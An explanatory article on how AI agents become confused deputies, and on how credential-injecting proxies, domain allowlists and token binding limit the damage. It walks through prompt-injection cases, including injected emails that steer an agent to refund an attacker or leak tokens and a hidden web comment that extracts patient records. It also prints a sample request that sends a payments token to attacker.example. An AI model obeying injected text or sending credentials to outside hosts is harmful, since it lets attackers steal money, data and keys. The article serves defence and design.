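# Domain allowlists for AI agents' authenticated requests: what they prevent and how they fail

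## What is a confused deputy, and why can an AI agent become one?

A confused deputy is a program that uses its own authority for someone who has no right to it. Engineers met the problem on the timeshared computers of the 1970s, and it has returned with AI agents, programs in which a language model repeatedly chooses an action, carries it out through a tool and reads the result. Many of these actions are requests to other companies' services, which act only for authorized callers, so the people who run an agent lend it some of their own rights. They also let it read web pages, documents and emails written by strangers. One common safeguard is a domain allowlist, which lets requests go only to the host names on the list.

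An online shop might use an assistant to work through customer emails. Staff ask it to summarize the morning's complaints or reply to someone whose parcel never came. It can look up charges and issue refunds through a payments service, and read the shop's inbox and send from it through a mail service. It also has an account on a code host, the site where the shop's developers keep their source code, so that it can file a bug when a customer reports that the checkout page is broken. Each of these permissions has an ordinary use, but anyone can write to the inbox.

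### Credentials and authenticated requests

The payments service cannot see who sits at the other end of a connection. It relies on a credential: a secret, such as an API key or access token, that a service accepts as proof of who is calling. A request that carries one is an authenticated request, and the service carries it out with the credential owner's rights. In HTTP, the protocol of the web, a request to look up one charge might read:

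```
GET /charges/1042 HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer EXAMPLE-TOKEN
```

The top line gives the requested resource, the middle line the host, and the bottom line the credential. The layout follows *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the internet standard for this kind of credential. The standard defines a bearer token as one that any holder can use in the same ways as any other holder. The holder doesn't have to prove anything else, so a copy works as well as the original. The standard therefore requires encryption in transit and advises against putting the token in the web address, because servers tend to log addresses.

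A token has a limited scope and lifetime, so the shop could ask for one that permits only refunds and expires in an hour. Within that scope, the service serves any request that carries a valid token. The three lines above don't record who wanted the charge looked up or why.

A domain allowlist for the assistant would contain the host names of the payments service, the mail service and the code host. The simplest kind of allowlist checks only a request's host name, so it would allow the request above and block requests to hosts not on the list.

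### Hardy's compiler

The term comes from Norm Hardy's short 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, which tells what he called a "nearly true story" from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler, a program that turns source code into something a machine can run, was stored in a directory called SYSX. The engineers wanted statistics on which language features people used, so the compiler recorded them in a file in the same directory, (SYSX)STAT. To let it write there, the engineers gave it a privilege called "home files license", which let a program write files in its own home directory.

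Anyone who ran the compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. One user learned that SYSX held a file called (SYSX)BILL, which contained Tymshare's billing records, and supplied that name. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file for output, and the operating system allowed this because the compiler had its license for SYSX. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

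No one in this story clearly broke a rule. The user typed a file name where the compiler accepts file names. The compiler put its output where the user said, and the operating system applied the license as its designers intended. Hardy considers the obvious patches and finds a problem with each. The compiler cannot refuse file names in other directories, since people have good reasons to send output there. It cannot refuse SYSX, because that name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code, and someone with legitimate access might want a file there. Banning the name BILL would protect only one of several sensitive files, and somebody would have to extend the ban for each new one. On Hardy's account, the code was correct when it was written and became wrong when the engineers added the license. To notice this, they would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote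 a file.

In the original story, Tymshare's compiler had no need to write to BILL. It could do so because the engineers had given it write access to a whole directory to solve a problem with one file. API keys often grant similarly broad access, so the original is closer to the shop's position than the retellings, which tend to simplify it. In *Capability Myths Demolished*, for example, Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003) give the compiler write access to BILL so that it can store bills, and they acknowledge the simplification in a footnote.

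### Ambient authority and the remedy

Hardy traced the problem to the compiler having two sources of authority, the user who ran it and the license. The compiler could not specify which one it was using for a given write. Miller and colleagues call this ambient authority. It applies to everything a program does, without the program selecting which right to use or stating for whom. They compare it to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens for certain people. Unix file permissions work this way. A program requests a file by name without presenting a credential, and the call succeeds or fails.

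Tymshare first tried a system call for switching hats, which let the compiler declare that it was now acting only on the user's authority. A request for BILL would then have correctly failed. But some applications soon needed more than two hats, there were kinds of authority other than file access, and the changes spread through the system. Meanwhile, the rules for opening a file had grown to fourteen boolean operators.

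Hardy's preferred remedy was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and carries the right to write to it. The system gives the compiler a capability for STAT. A user who wants debugging output gives the compiler a capability for one of their own files, and the compiler uses that capability to write the output. A user with no right to write to BILL has no capability for it to hand over, and knowing the file's name doesn't help. UT Austin's lecture slides *The Confused Deputy* describe a modern Unix equivalent, in which the program that launches the compiler opens the debug file under its own limited rights and passes the open file to the compiler.

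Capabilities remove the split between naming a resource and having the right to use it. In Tymshare's case, one party chose the file and another party's authority opened it. Miller and colleagues expect confusion wherever the name and the right arrive separately and are combined later. They don't claim that capabilities prevent all confusion. A program that holds several keys and tries each until one works can still be confused. Researchers disputed for years whether capabilities really differ from ordinary access lists. Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016), in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, proved in a formal model that the two are fundamentally different, and gave the first formal definition of a program free of confused deputy attacks.

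An agent's web request can combine parts from different sources, as in the Tymshare case. The address may come from an email that the agent has just read, while the credential comes from the shop. The split is clearest when a separate program, a credential-injecting proxy, adds the credential after the agent has composed the request. In Help Net Security's *The first ten lines of a command policy for AI coding agents* (2026), Vinay Thakker of the company KloudStax describes a proxy that does this for every request as "a confused deputy waiting for instructions". Some researchers have applied the capability idea to agents, but ambient authority seems to be usual. In *Delegation Without Trust*, Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) looked at the default settings of three popular agent frameworks, LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen, and found no built-in limit on how an agent uses its authority. They ran LangGraph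 with a script in place of the model and inspected the code of the other two. Both work for a vendor of agent security, which is a reason for some caution, though the finding is modest, since none of the three frameworks claims to be an authorisation system.

### When the user lacks the right

A formal version of the problem for agents appears in Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*. Let R be the set of permissions in a system, so that a pair (a, b) in R means that a may access b. A confused deputy attack occurs when the agent accesses some target and

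(user, target) ∉ R, while (agent, target) ∈ R.

Like the compiler, the agent uses its own access to reach a resource that the user isn't allowed to reach. In their example, an employee without access to the personnel database asks for everyone's salary. The agent has access for administrative work, and it runs the query.

The security firm Quarkslab demonstrated the same flaw with a small medical assistant whose lookup tool accepted any patient number the model gave it. A logged-in patient asked for another patient's history and got it. Quarkslab then added a line to the model's standing instructions limiting it to the current patient's records, and the same request failed. But when the assistant read a web page with a hidden comment asking for the other patient's data, it printed the record again. Changing the tool fixed the flaw. The tool now either compares the requested number with the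 logged-in patient's or takes the number from the login session so that the model never supplies it, which protects other patients' records even if the model obeys a hidden comment. The demonstration used a small model from 2024, so it is weak evidence of how often a current model would obey such a comment.

### When the orders come from outside

The employee who asks the shop's assistant to summarize the inbox is entitled to issue refunds and read the code, but a customer, or someone posing as one, can send an email containing instructions addressed to the assistant. This is prompt injection, in which text in the material an agent processes makes it follow someone else's instructions. Willison, who coined the term, explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that language models follow instructions in whatever content reaches them and cannot reliably rank those instructions by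 origin. He calls email a perfect source of untrusted text because an attacker can write to the agent directly.

Siu and colleagues define this case separately, as indirect prompt injection, and they require two things of it. Some source of the instruction that the agent followed must be unauthenticated, and the resulting action must fail to serve the user's task:

source ∉ S_auth, and H(action) = 0.

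S_auth is the set of authenticated sources, and H is a judgement of whether the action serves the task (1 for yes, 0 for no). The second condition is needed because agents often should follow directions from strangers. For example, if a user tells an agent to follow a recipe on a website, the agent should use the oven temperature the recipe gives. But if an agent is asked to summarise an email, and the email tells it to send out all the customer data, that instruction meets both conditions. The paper acknowledges that H is an ideal. Real systems can only approximate it with rules or another model.

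The framework doesn't settle one case between these two. A user asks an agent to order ingredients, and the recipe page names the payment card to use. Siu and colleagues call this a violation because an outsider picked the card. But they also say the purchase serves the task, and their combined formula allows an unauthenticated source whenever the action serves the task, so it would allow this purchase. The shop could face the same problem if an employee really did request a refund but an email supplied the account number.

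Under the narrow definition, the shop's assistant is not a confused deputy, because (employee, payments) is in R. The definition does fit if the email's author, rather than the employee, counts as the user. Dantuluri and Sundi use the term in this wider sense, for any agent that injected content steers into using legitimate authority for an attacker's goal. They summarize it as "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended." The wider sense also seems the better reading of Hardy, because the problem at Tymshare was that the person who chose the file had no right to it.

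The distinction affects the choice of fix. In the salary case, it is enough to limit the agent to what the user is allowed to do. That limit doesn't protect the shop, because the employee is allowed to do everything the attacker wants.

### Why a model stays confusable

Tymshare could in principle have fixed its compiler, but David C doubts that anyone can do the same for a language model. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, he compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers fixed SQL injection with parameterised queries, which keep the typed text separate from the command so that the database never runs it as one. A language model has no equivalent separation, because it receives instructions and data as a single sequence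 of tokens and predicts the next token. He therefore calls such systems "inherently confusable" and tells designers to plan for the worst case, in which an attacker can do anything that direct access to the agent's tools would allow. He advises relying on safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do. A domain allowlist is one such safeguard, since it allows or blocks a given host regardless of how the model interpreted its input.

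Models have become much harder to fool since he wrote. In a test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers who had fifteen attempts succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases and against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in 20.0%, according to Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026). A single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* adds that no attack worked in 129 browser scenarios. These results come from Anthropic's own system card, the report a developer publishes with a model, and an independent repetition would be welcome. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 resisted direct injection well but did worse when the attack arrived through tools and outside content, which is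 how it would reach the shop. A 2% success rate is a great improvement, but it is still worrying for an assistant that can send money, because an attacker can easily send more emails. Schneier on Security also says that prompt injection is impossible to prevent in the general case.

### Three kinds of harm

If an injected email gets through, the shop's loss depends on what the attacker wants, and a defence against one kind of loss can be useless against another.

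An attacker may only want to use the assistant's authority, for example to issue a refund to their own account or delete a repository. In these cases, the token isn't stolen and no private data leaves the shop. Siu and colleagues classify such acts, including redirected funds, as integrity violations, separate from leaks. These acts can also be hard to spot afterwards. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn’t give an AI agent unlimited authority* reports that when an agent works through a shared administrator account, the log shows the account but not who wanted the change. The same article describes a test in which an agent tried to grant access on its own after a tester mentioned a deadline, so this kind of misuse can happen without an attacker.

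The attacker may instead want data, such as the shop's customer list or private source code. Exfiltration means moving data to a place where an unauthorised person can read it. The assistant reads the data with rights it properly holds and then sends it to such a place, so the attacker never needs the token.

The remaining possibility is that the attacker steals the credential itself. If the assistant can read its payments token, an attacker can inject an instruction to repeat the token in an outgoing message. A bearer token works for anyone who presents it, so an attacker who receives it can call the payments service from their own machine, within the token's scope, until it expires or the shop revokes it. A domain allowlist on the assistant's traffic can't block those calls, because they don't pass through it.

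## How can an agent use a credential it never sees?

An attacker can't trick the shop's assistant into repeating a token it doesn't have. But the payments service still requires the token, so a credential-injecting proxy outside the agent's environment adds it to each request. Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents*, a guide for companies that run agents on its software, recommends this pattern. Infisical's *Credential Brokering for AI Agents, Explained* lists Vercel, Cloudflare and LangChain among the companies that have built versions of it. Infisical, which sells software for storing secrets, also maintains Agent Vault, an open-source proxy of this kind.

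### One request through the proxy

Suppose an employee asks the assistant to look up charge 1042. The assistant has no payments token. It has a placeholder, a dummy string that stands where the token would go, and it writes:

```
GET /charges/1042 HTTP/1.1
Host: api.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer PAYMENTS-PLACEHOLDER
```

The assistant could also leave out the last line and let the proxy write it. Placeholders are useful because some programs won't start without a key, and some check the key's format, as Docker's *Manage credentials* points out.

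The `HTTPS_PROXY` setting directs the assistant's web client to the proxy instead of the payments service. With Agent Vault, the assistant identifies itself to the proxy with a session token. The proxy decrypts the request, finds its rule for `api.payments.example` and looks up the real token. It replaces the placeholder with the real token, encrypts the request again and forwards it. The payments service receives a request ending in `Bearer EXAMPLE-TOKEN` and treats it like any other authenticated request. The reply comes back through the proxy, and the assistant reads the charge.

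So the assistant does hold one secret, its session token, but an attacker who steals it gains much less than one who steals the payments token. Infisical's *Security & Architecture*, which documents a product that Infisical has since replaced with Agent Vault, explains that an attacker can't use the agent's token to fetch a stored secret, only to send traffic through the proxy to services the agent could already reach. Infisical advises operators to keep the proxy on a private network, because anyone on the internet could try to make authenticated calls through a public one.

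### Why the proxy has to decrypt

An ordinary web proxy can't add a credential to an HTTPS request. The client uses an HTTP command called CONNECT to ask the proxy to open a connection to a named host. The proxy opens it and then copies bytes in both directions. Over this connection, the client and the service set up encryption with TLS, the protocol that protects HTTPS traffic. The proxy knows which host the client asked for, but the `Authorization` line is encrypted, so the proxy can't read the placeholder. If it changed any bytes, the service would detect the change and drop the connection.

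The proxy therefore needs TLS termination, which means decrypting traffic so that it can read or change the request before encrypting it again. This creates two encrypted connections, one from the assistant to the proxy and one from the proxy to the payments service. On the first connection, the proxy has to identify itself as the payments service. A web client normally accepts a server only if the server presents a certificate for the right host name, signed by an authority the client trusts. The operator therefore has to create a new authority and add it to the list of those that the agent's environment trusts.

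In Infisical's older proxy, for example, the certificate authority's main key stays on Infisical's server and signs a seven-day certificate for the proxy. The proxy uses that certificate to sign a 24-hour certificate for each host name an agent requests. A launcher program on the agent's machine downloads the main certificate and sets six environment variables that point to it, because different programs read different variables. The proxy connects to the real service with the normal certificate checks, so the credential still travels encrypted.

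A simpler method works for a single service. Anthropic's software has a setting for the address where it sends model requests. An operator can set this to a proxy on the same machine, which receives the requests unencrypted, adds the key and forwards them over HTTPS. This method does not require installing a new certificate authority, but it covers only requests to the model.

### Programs that ignore the proxy

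`HTTPS_PROXY` is a convention that programs can ignore. Anthropic lists curl, pip, npm and git among the tools that follow it. Node.js, a common way to run JavaScript outside a browser, has a built-in `fetch()` function that ignores it by default, though newer versions have a switch to change this.

If the shop's assistant runs a script that ignores the setting, the request goes straight to the payments service with the placeholder still in it. The service rejects it, and the employee sees a puzzling login error. More seriously, a script that bypasses the proxy also avoids its domain allowlist and log, so it could send the customer list anywhere without the proxy recording it. An attacker who can get the agent to run code can choose a program that ignores the setting, or unset the variable.

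The operator has to block every route out except the proxy. Anthropic gives the example of a container, an isolated environment for running programs, that has no network connection. Its only way out is a socket, a local communication channel, connected to a proxy on the host machine, so any attempt to connect directly fails. The operating system can instead redirect all outgoing connections to a proxy, whether or not the program knows about it. Either way, the proxy still has to terminate TLS.

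Not every product closes these routes for the operator. Infisical states that Agent Vault does not sandbox the agent and suggests pairing it with something that does. The company also prefers to run the proxy on a separate machine. Two containers on one machine share a kernel, the core of the operating system, and a flaw in it could let the agent reach the proxy's secrets. ZenML's tutorial *Credential proxy* is less strict and puts the token only in a separate container. That is a reasonable start for a low-value token, but the shop's token is more valuable because it can issue refunds.

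### A tool that makes the call itself

An operator can avoid decrypting the agent's traffic by giving the agent a custom tool instead of letting it write web requests to the service. For example, the agent might pass a charge number to a "look up a charge" tool. A program outside the sandbox receives the number, composes the request, adds the credential or has a proxy add it, and returns the result. In Anthropic's example, the agent gives a command to a tool for git, the program developers use to manage source code, and a proxy on the host machine adds the login before contacting the code-hosting service.

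A custom tool can also be much more limited than a general web request. If the shop's tool only looks up charges, the agent can't use it to issue a refund, whatever instructions it reads in an email. The tool's author can also set parts of the request in code so the agent can't change them, as Quarkslab did when it took the patient number from the login session.

However, someone has to write and maintain a tool for every service, and existing programs aren't built to use it. For that reason, Infisical argues that agents should keep using their usual command-line tools while the proxy works in the background. A custom tool seems better for the shop, which needs only a few operations from its payments service. A coding agent that runs dozens of programs would be hard to equip this way.

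### Four designs compared

OpenAI offers credential injection in a hosted environment where its models can run commands. The environment has no outside network access by default. According to OpenAI's *Shell*, an administrator must first approve a list of domains for the organization, and a developer then selects from it for each request. The `domain_secrets` feature attaches a credential to one of the selected domains. The model and its environment see a name such as `$API_KEY`, and a separate program, which OpenAI calls an auth-translation sidecar, replaces that name with the credential only for approved destinations.

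Anthropic's guide describes an architecture that operators assemble themselves. It suggests existing software such as Envoy, a general-purpose proxy with a component for adding credentials, or mitmproxy, which specializes in decrypting and changing HTTPS traffic. How credentials are injected therefore depends on the software the operator chooses.

Docker makes a sandbox for running agents on a developer's computer. Its proxy runs on the host and usually reads credentials from the operating system's keychain. For services that Docker or an add-on has defined, the proxy overwrites the authentication header, and the sandbox holds only a marker such as `proxy-managed`. For other services, a developer can set up a "custom secret" with a random placeholder, a feature that Docker still labels experimental. The proxy doesn't add these credentials to unencrypted HTTP requests. Docker also has an option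 to pass a real login token into the sandbox, but warns that this reduces isolation.

With Agent Vault, an operator groups services into an "access bundle" and grants it to an agent for a limited session. The operator can restrict a service to certain HTTP methods and paths, for example to let an agent read charges but not create refunds. If someone revokes the session, running agents lose access within about a minute by default.

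| Design | What the agent's environment holds | Where the real credential goes | Does the vendor document masking of replies? |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, `domain_secrets` | A named placeholder | An authorization header in the example; no rule given for other parts | No |
| Anthropic, deployment guide | No credential | Depends on the chosen proxy | No |
| Docker, defined services | A fixed marker | The header in the service's definition | No |
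| Docker, custom secrets | A random placeholder | Configured headers only | Yes, with exceptions |
| Infisical, Agent Vault | A session token, and sometimes a placeholder | A header, or wherever the operator allows the placeholder | No |

### When a service repeats the credential

The proxy keeps the credential out of the request the agent writes, but the agent also reads the reply. If the service includes the credential in its reply, the agent now has it.

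OpenAI's own example for `domain_secrets` sends a request to `httpbin.org/headers`, a page on a public site for testing web clients that returns the headers of any request it receives. The model puts the placeholder `$API_KEY` in the authorization header, and the user asks it to report what it sees. The sidecar replaces the placeholder with the real value on the way out, so httpbin returns the real value. Yet OpenAI also states that raw secret values don't appear in anything the model can see. Both can be true only if something removes the value from the reply, and OpenAI doesn't describe such a step. The value in the example is a dummy, `debug-secret-123`, so a developer can safely run the example and check whether the model reports the placeholder or the dummy.

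An ordinary service is more likely than httpbin to expose a valuable credential, since few operators would give httpbin one. The service might have an error message or debugging page that repeats the request's headers. The proxy can defend against this by response scrubbing, which means searching each reply for the credentials it has just inserted and masking them before the agent receives it.

Docker's documentation describes a proxy that checks a reply's headers and body for the original value of a custom secret and three common encodings of it. The proxy returns an error instead of passing on a partial reply or one in a compression format it can't read, since either could hide the value. Docker says the filter can't guarantee secrecy. It doesn't inspect WebSocket messages, which travel over a connection that stays open in both directions, and it can miss a secret that the service splits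 across several fields. Masking the secret can also leave a reply that the client program can't parse.

The filter doesn't apply to the defined services, which Docker tells developers to use whenever they can. Docker doesn't explain this exemption, but it may matter little in practice because those are mostly large services that are unlikely to repeat a key. Anthropic doesn't mention scrubbing, so an operator who follows its guide would need to check whether the chosen proxy does it, or add it. Infisical's overview of Agent Vault doesn't mention it either, although its *How Agent Vault Works* claims there is "no point on the wire" that returns the real values to the agent. A service that repeats the request headers in its reply would return them unless the proxy masks the reply.

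An operator can reduce the risk without scrubbing. Before adding a service to the allowlist for a credential, the operator can send it a few requests containing a dummy value, including some malformed requests, and search the replies for that value. Using a short-lived token also limits the damage if the token leaks.

### Why the placeholder's position matters

In the example request, the placeholder is in the `Authorization` header. The payments service uses that header to identify the caller and has little reason to store it or show it to anyone. But services often pass on text from the body of a request to other people.

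An attacker can steal the mail token if the proxy replaces its placeholder anywhere in a request to the shop's mail service. Suppose an email with injected instructions gets the assistant to include the placeholder in the text of a message to the attacker. The assistant sends only the placeholder, but the proxy replaces it with the real token, and the mail service delivers the message. The allowlist doesn't stop this, because the request goes to an approved host and carries a credential meant for that host. Scrubbing the mail service's reply wouldn't help either, because the attacker reads the token in their own inbox. The code host's token can leak the same way if the assistant puts its placeholder in a public bug report.

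The fix is for the proxy to replace the placeholder only in a specific header. Docker does this for custom secrets, and sends the placeholder unchanged if it appears in the body or any other header. An even simpler fix is for the proxy to overwrite the header, ignoring what the agent wrote there.

Infisical's introduction to Agent Vault presents it as an advantage that the proxy swaps the placeholder "wherever it appears in the outbound request", so no one has to configure it for each service's login method. Some services expect the key in the web address or the body. Infisical's documentation for the older proxy is more cautious. The operator lists the parts of the request that the proxy will search (path, query, header or body), and Infisical warns that "Scoping is the security boundary". The shop should list only the header for its mail service. If a service accepts a key only in the body,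 a custom tool that writes the entire body is safer than general substitution. A key in the path or query can be exposed if a server logs the address.

### All the secrets in one place

A proxy that serves many agents needs access to all their credentials. Infisical's ready-made role for its older proxy lets it read every secret value in a project, though an operator can define a narrower role. Anyone who takes over the proxy's machine gets whatever the proxy can read. In return, the operator has to protect one machine instead of a token on every machine that runs an agent.

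The usual example of this risk is a March 2026 attack on LiteLLM, an open-source gateway through which a company's programs can reach many AI models. LiteLLM holds the company's API keys for the model providers, and Anthropic's guide lists it as one way to inject credentials. On 24 March, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM on PyPI, the main public index of Python packages. They had obtained a publishing token through an earlier attack on Trivy, a security scanner used in LiteLLM's release process. The malicious code searched for cloud credentials, SSH keys, database passwords and the contents of environment variables, where programs often keep API keys. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the code sent what it found to a domain that resembled LiteLLM's own.

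Accounts of the scale differ. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) puts the exposure at 2 hours and 32 minutes, with over 119,000 downloads. LiteLLM says the versions were available for about 40 minutes, and FutureSearch counted 46,996 downloads in 46 minutes from PyPI's download logs. The download rates are fairly similar, at about 780 a minute on PyPI's figures and 1,020 on FutureSearch's, so most of the difference in downloads comes from the length of the window. PyPI removed the packages itself, which is a reason to prefer its account, but FutureSearch gives a clock time for each step, and LiteLLM's estimate is close to FutureSearch's. The download counts are not counts of victims, because automated systems download the same package many times.

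Hartman, an instructor at the security training organization SANS, writes in *Your AI Agent Is an Easily Confused Deputy* that the attack affected an estimated 500,000 corporate identities, a much larger number, but he gives no source. He also says the attack succeeded because LiteLLM kept so many long-lived credentials in one place. The other accounts support only part of this. The attackers got in through the release process, and their code took whatever it found on any machine that installed the package, whether or not the machine ran a gateway. Companies that used LiteLLM's official container image for the gateway were unaffected because the image fixes the exact versions of the packages it includes. Keeping so many keys in one place does explain why a gateway is an attractive target and why an infected one would do so much damage. Datadog Security Labs advises treating every credential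 on an affected machine as exposed.

The shop can fix the versions of everything its proxy installs, as the official image does. PyPI also recommends waiting, for example, three days before installing a new release. This would have kept out both malicious versions, though urgent security fixes need an exception. A firewall that lets the proxy's machine reach only the services it needs would probably have stopped the upload to the attackers' domain.

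Hartman has submitted a draft internet standard that goes further and splits the job between two components. One decides whether an agent may have access but holds no credentials. The other issues credentials, but only on signed approvals from the first. The agent receives a token that lasts seconds or minutes and is tied to a cryptographic key. Unlike a bearer token, it can't be used without that key, even if someone copies it. An attacker who controls the deciding component can still approve requests but can't read any stored secrets. The split gives less protection against an attacker who controls the issuing component, who could then create tokens without approval.

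### Using a secret without having it

SSH, a protocol for logging in to remote machines, has long had a similar arrangement. A program called an SSH agent holds the private key and signs login requests for other programs. Docker can connect its sandbox to the SSH agent on the host, and says that programs in the sandbox can request signatures but can't read or copy the key. While a malicious program is running in the sandbox, though, it can use those signatures to log in as the developer on any server that the sandbox's network rules let it reach.

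An attacker can also misuse the shop's payments token without the assistant ever seeing it. Infisical says that with its proxy there is "nothing for an injected instruction to exfiltrate", which is fair for the credential but doesn't cover the customer list or refunds. If an injected email leads the assistant to refund an attacker, the assistant writes a refund request with the placeholder in the usual header. The proxy recognizes the assistant's session, finds a rule for the payments service and adds the real token, because nothing in the request shows that the email prompted it.

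## What does tying a credential to approved domains prevent?

If a proxy adds a token only to requests for approved domains, a refund request carrying that token at least goes to the service the token is for. A proxy with no domain limit would add the token to a request for any server, including an attacker's.

Suppose a customer's email tells the assistant to confirm the shop's payment settings with a server that the attacker runs. The assistant follows the instruction and writes:

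```
POST /confirm HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example
Authorization: Bearer PAYMENTS-PLACEHOLDER
```

The proxy replaces the placeholder with the real payments token and forwards the request, and the attacker reads the token in the server's log. Hiding the token from the assistant doesn't prevent this theft. Encryption doesn't either, because the attacker's server can have a valid certificate for its own domain name, and TLS then protects the token only on its way to that server. A filter that searches the assistant's outgoing text for secrets would find only the placeholder.

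*The Attack You as an AI Agent Developer Haven't Thought About Yet*, by The Seventeen, describes this attack and proposes the company's own open-source proxy, AgentSecrets, as the solution. Code that uses AgentSecrets passes it a web address and the name of a key. As at Tymshare, the two can come from different parties.

### Checking before the lookup

The fix is a domain check inside the proxy. For each request, the proxy should:

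1. read the destination host from the decrypted request;
2. refuse the request unless the operator has approved that host for the credential;
3. fetch the credential from its store;
4. add the credential and forward the request to the host it has just checked.

AgentSecrets also checks the domain of each call before its proxy looks up the key, and it refuses the call at that point if the operator hasn't added the domain to its list.

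If the proxy checks the host before fetching the token, a rejected request contains only the placeholder. A proxy that fetched the token first would still keep it from the attacker if everything worked, but it would briefly hold a rejected request with the real token in it. Programs often write rejected requests to error logs or crash reports, and some repeat them in error messages, which the assistant might read.

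If the proxy obtains a new short-lived token for each request, checking the domain first also prevents it from obtaining tokens for requests to unapproved domains. The secret store's access log stays cleaner too, since it records only lookups for approved destinations.

### Where traffic may go and where each key may go

An operator can restrict an agent's requests by domain in two ways. A network allowlist limits where the agent's traffic may go, whether or not a request carries a credential. With credential binding, the proxy adds a credential only to requests for the domains listed for that credential.

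OpenAI separates the choice of which hosts an environment may reach from the choice of which hosts get a credential. The `allowed_domains` setting lists the reachable hosts. In one of OpenAI's examples, it contains `github.com` and two hosts for downloading Python packages, and no secrets. With `domain_secrets`, a developer can allow five hosts and attach a key to only one of them.

The AgentSecrets example is less strict. Its commands add the addresses of Stripe, a payments company, and SendGrid, an email company, to one list for the whole workspace. The Seventeen doesn't mention a rule that would stop the proxy from sending the Stripe key to SendGrid.

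The shop needs both credential binding and a network allowlist. If it only binds credentials to domains, an injected instruction could still make the assistant post the customer list to the attacker's server, because that request needs no credential. A network allowlist stops the assistant from reaching that server, but on its own it still lets the assistant send any key to any approved service.

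### Fifteen pairs or three

The shop's proxy holds three keys, for the payments service, the mail service and the code host. Suppose the network allowlist has five hosts:

- `api.payments.example`
- `api.mail.example`
- `api.code.example`
- `tracking.parcels.example`, where the assistant looks up late parcels
- `rates.bank.example`, where it finds exchange rates for foreign refunds

The last two hosts need no key. If the proxy uses this list for every key, it allows any of the three keys to go to any of the five hosts, which makes 3 × 5 = 15 permitted key-host pairs. If the operator binds each key to its own service, only 3 pairs are permitted.

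The difference between sharing one list across all keys and binding each key to its own host grows as the list gets longer. With ten keys and twenty hosts, a shared list permits 200 key-host pairs, while binding each key to one host permits 10. Some services use more than one host name, such as a separate one for uploads, and each extra host adds one pair, for that service's key only.

Some of the 12 pairs that binding removes are more dangerous than others. If the assistant sends the payments key to the code host in the usual header, the code host will probably reject the unfamiliar token, and the attacker won't see it. But another company has now received the key and may have logged it. The parcel company's website is more worrying, because a shared list makes every key only as safe as the least secure of the five hosts. An attacker who breaks into that site and plants instructions there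 could collect all three keys. With binding, the same attacker would receive none, because the operator has tied no key to that host.

Binding also limits the damage when a proxy replaces placeholders anywhere in a request. Under the shared list, even the payments key could end up in a public bug report. Binding prevents this, though the code host's own key could still leak this way.

Three injected requests show the difference between the two rules:

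| Injected request | One shared list of five hosts | Each key tied to its own service |
|---|---|---|
| Send the payments key to an unknown host | Blocked | Blocked |
| Send the payments key to the code host | Allowed | Blocked |
| Refund the attacker at the payments service | Allowed | Allowed |

In the second case, the proxy could also forward the request without the key. Refusing it seems better, because a request that sends the payments placeholder to the code host is almost certainly a mistake or an attack, and someone at the shop should know about it.

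The refund passes both rules because it sends the right key to the right host. The Seventeen claims that its proxy stops an attacker from redirecting the agent to use a key on the attacker's behalf. This is true for unlisted destinations but not for the refund. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* more accurately describes an allowlist as a "capability grant", because listing a domain gives an attacker access to every function reachable there. Stopping the refund requires checking the request itself as well as its destination.

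### Tokens that work at only one service

The proxy enforces credential binding, so binding has no effect on a key that has already leaked. Some credentials also have their own limits, which the receiving service enforces wherever the request comes from.

One such limit is an audience, the service or services where a token is valid. It matters most when one company issues tokens for several services. The shop's mail provider might also run a calendar and an address book with the same login. If a token works at all three, a compromised calendar service could use the token it receives to read the shop's mail.

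*Resource Indicators for OAuth 2.0*, an internet standard by Campbell, Bradley and Tschofenig, lets a program state where it intends to use a token when it requests one. The server that issues the token can then record that destination in it. Any other service should reject the token, so a calendar service should not be able to use a token it receives to access a mail service.

If a token has several audiences, any one of those services could use it at the others. The rights also multiply, much like the shop's 15 pairs. A token for two kinds of access at two services grants both kinds at both services, unless the issuer narrows it. Campbell and colleagues therefore encourage requesting one audience at a time. They also recommend making the audience specific enough to identify a tenant (one customer's separate account or workspace on a shared service). Otherwise, one tenant might use a token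 to reach another's data. The standard recommends that the issuer restrict the audience but doesn't require it, so the shop should check the tokens it receives.

An audience restriction doesn't protect the shop if the proxy sends the payments token to the attacker. A bearer token works for whoever holds it, and this one is valid at the payments service, where the attacker wants to use it. The restriction only stops the token from working at other services.

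### Tokens that need a second key

Hartman's draft ties each token to a cryptographic key. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)*, by Fett, Campbell and colleagues, already sets out a standard way to do this. The client, which would be the proxy in the shop's case, creates a pair of keys and keeps one private. The issuer ties the token to the public key. The proxy must then attach a new signed proof to every request. The proof contains the HTTP method, the web address without its query, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the token (a short value calculated from it). The service checks the signature and compares these details with the request it received.

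If the proxy mistakenly sends such a request to the attacker, the attacker receives the token and a proof for `attacker.example`. The payments service would reject that proof because it names the wrong address, and the attacker can't sign another without the private key. However, Fett and colleagues write that a service unaware of DPoP would probably accept the token as an ordinary bearer token. A service that supports both DPoP and bearer tokens must refuse to accept a DPoP token as a bearer token.

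The attacker can do more with a copy of a genuine request, perhaps from a log. The proof doesn't cover the body or most headers, so the attacker could reuse a proof for creating a refund and change the amount or the account number. The service should accept each proof only for seconds or minutes. It can also store each proof's identifier and reject repeats, which gives very strong protection but may be impractical when several servers handle the same address without sharing records.

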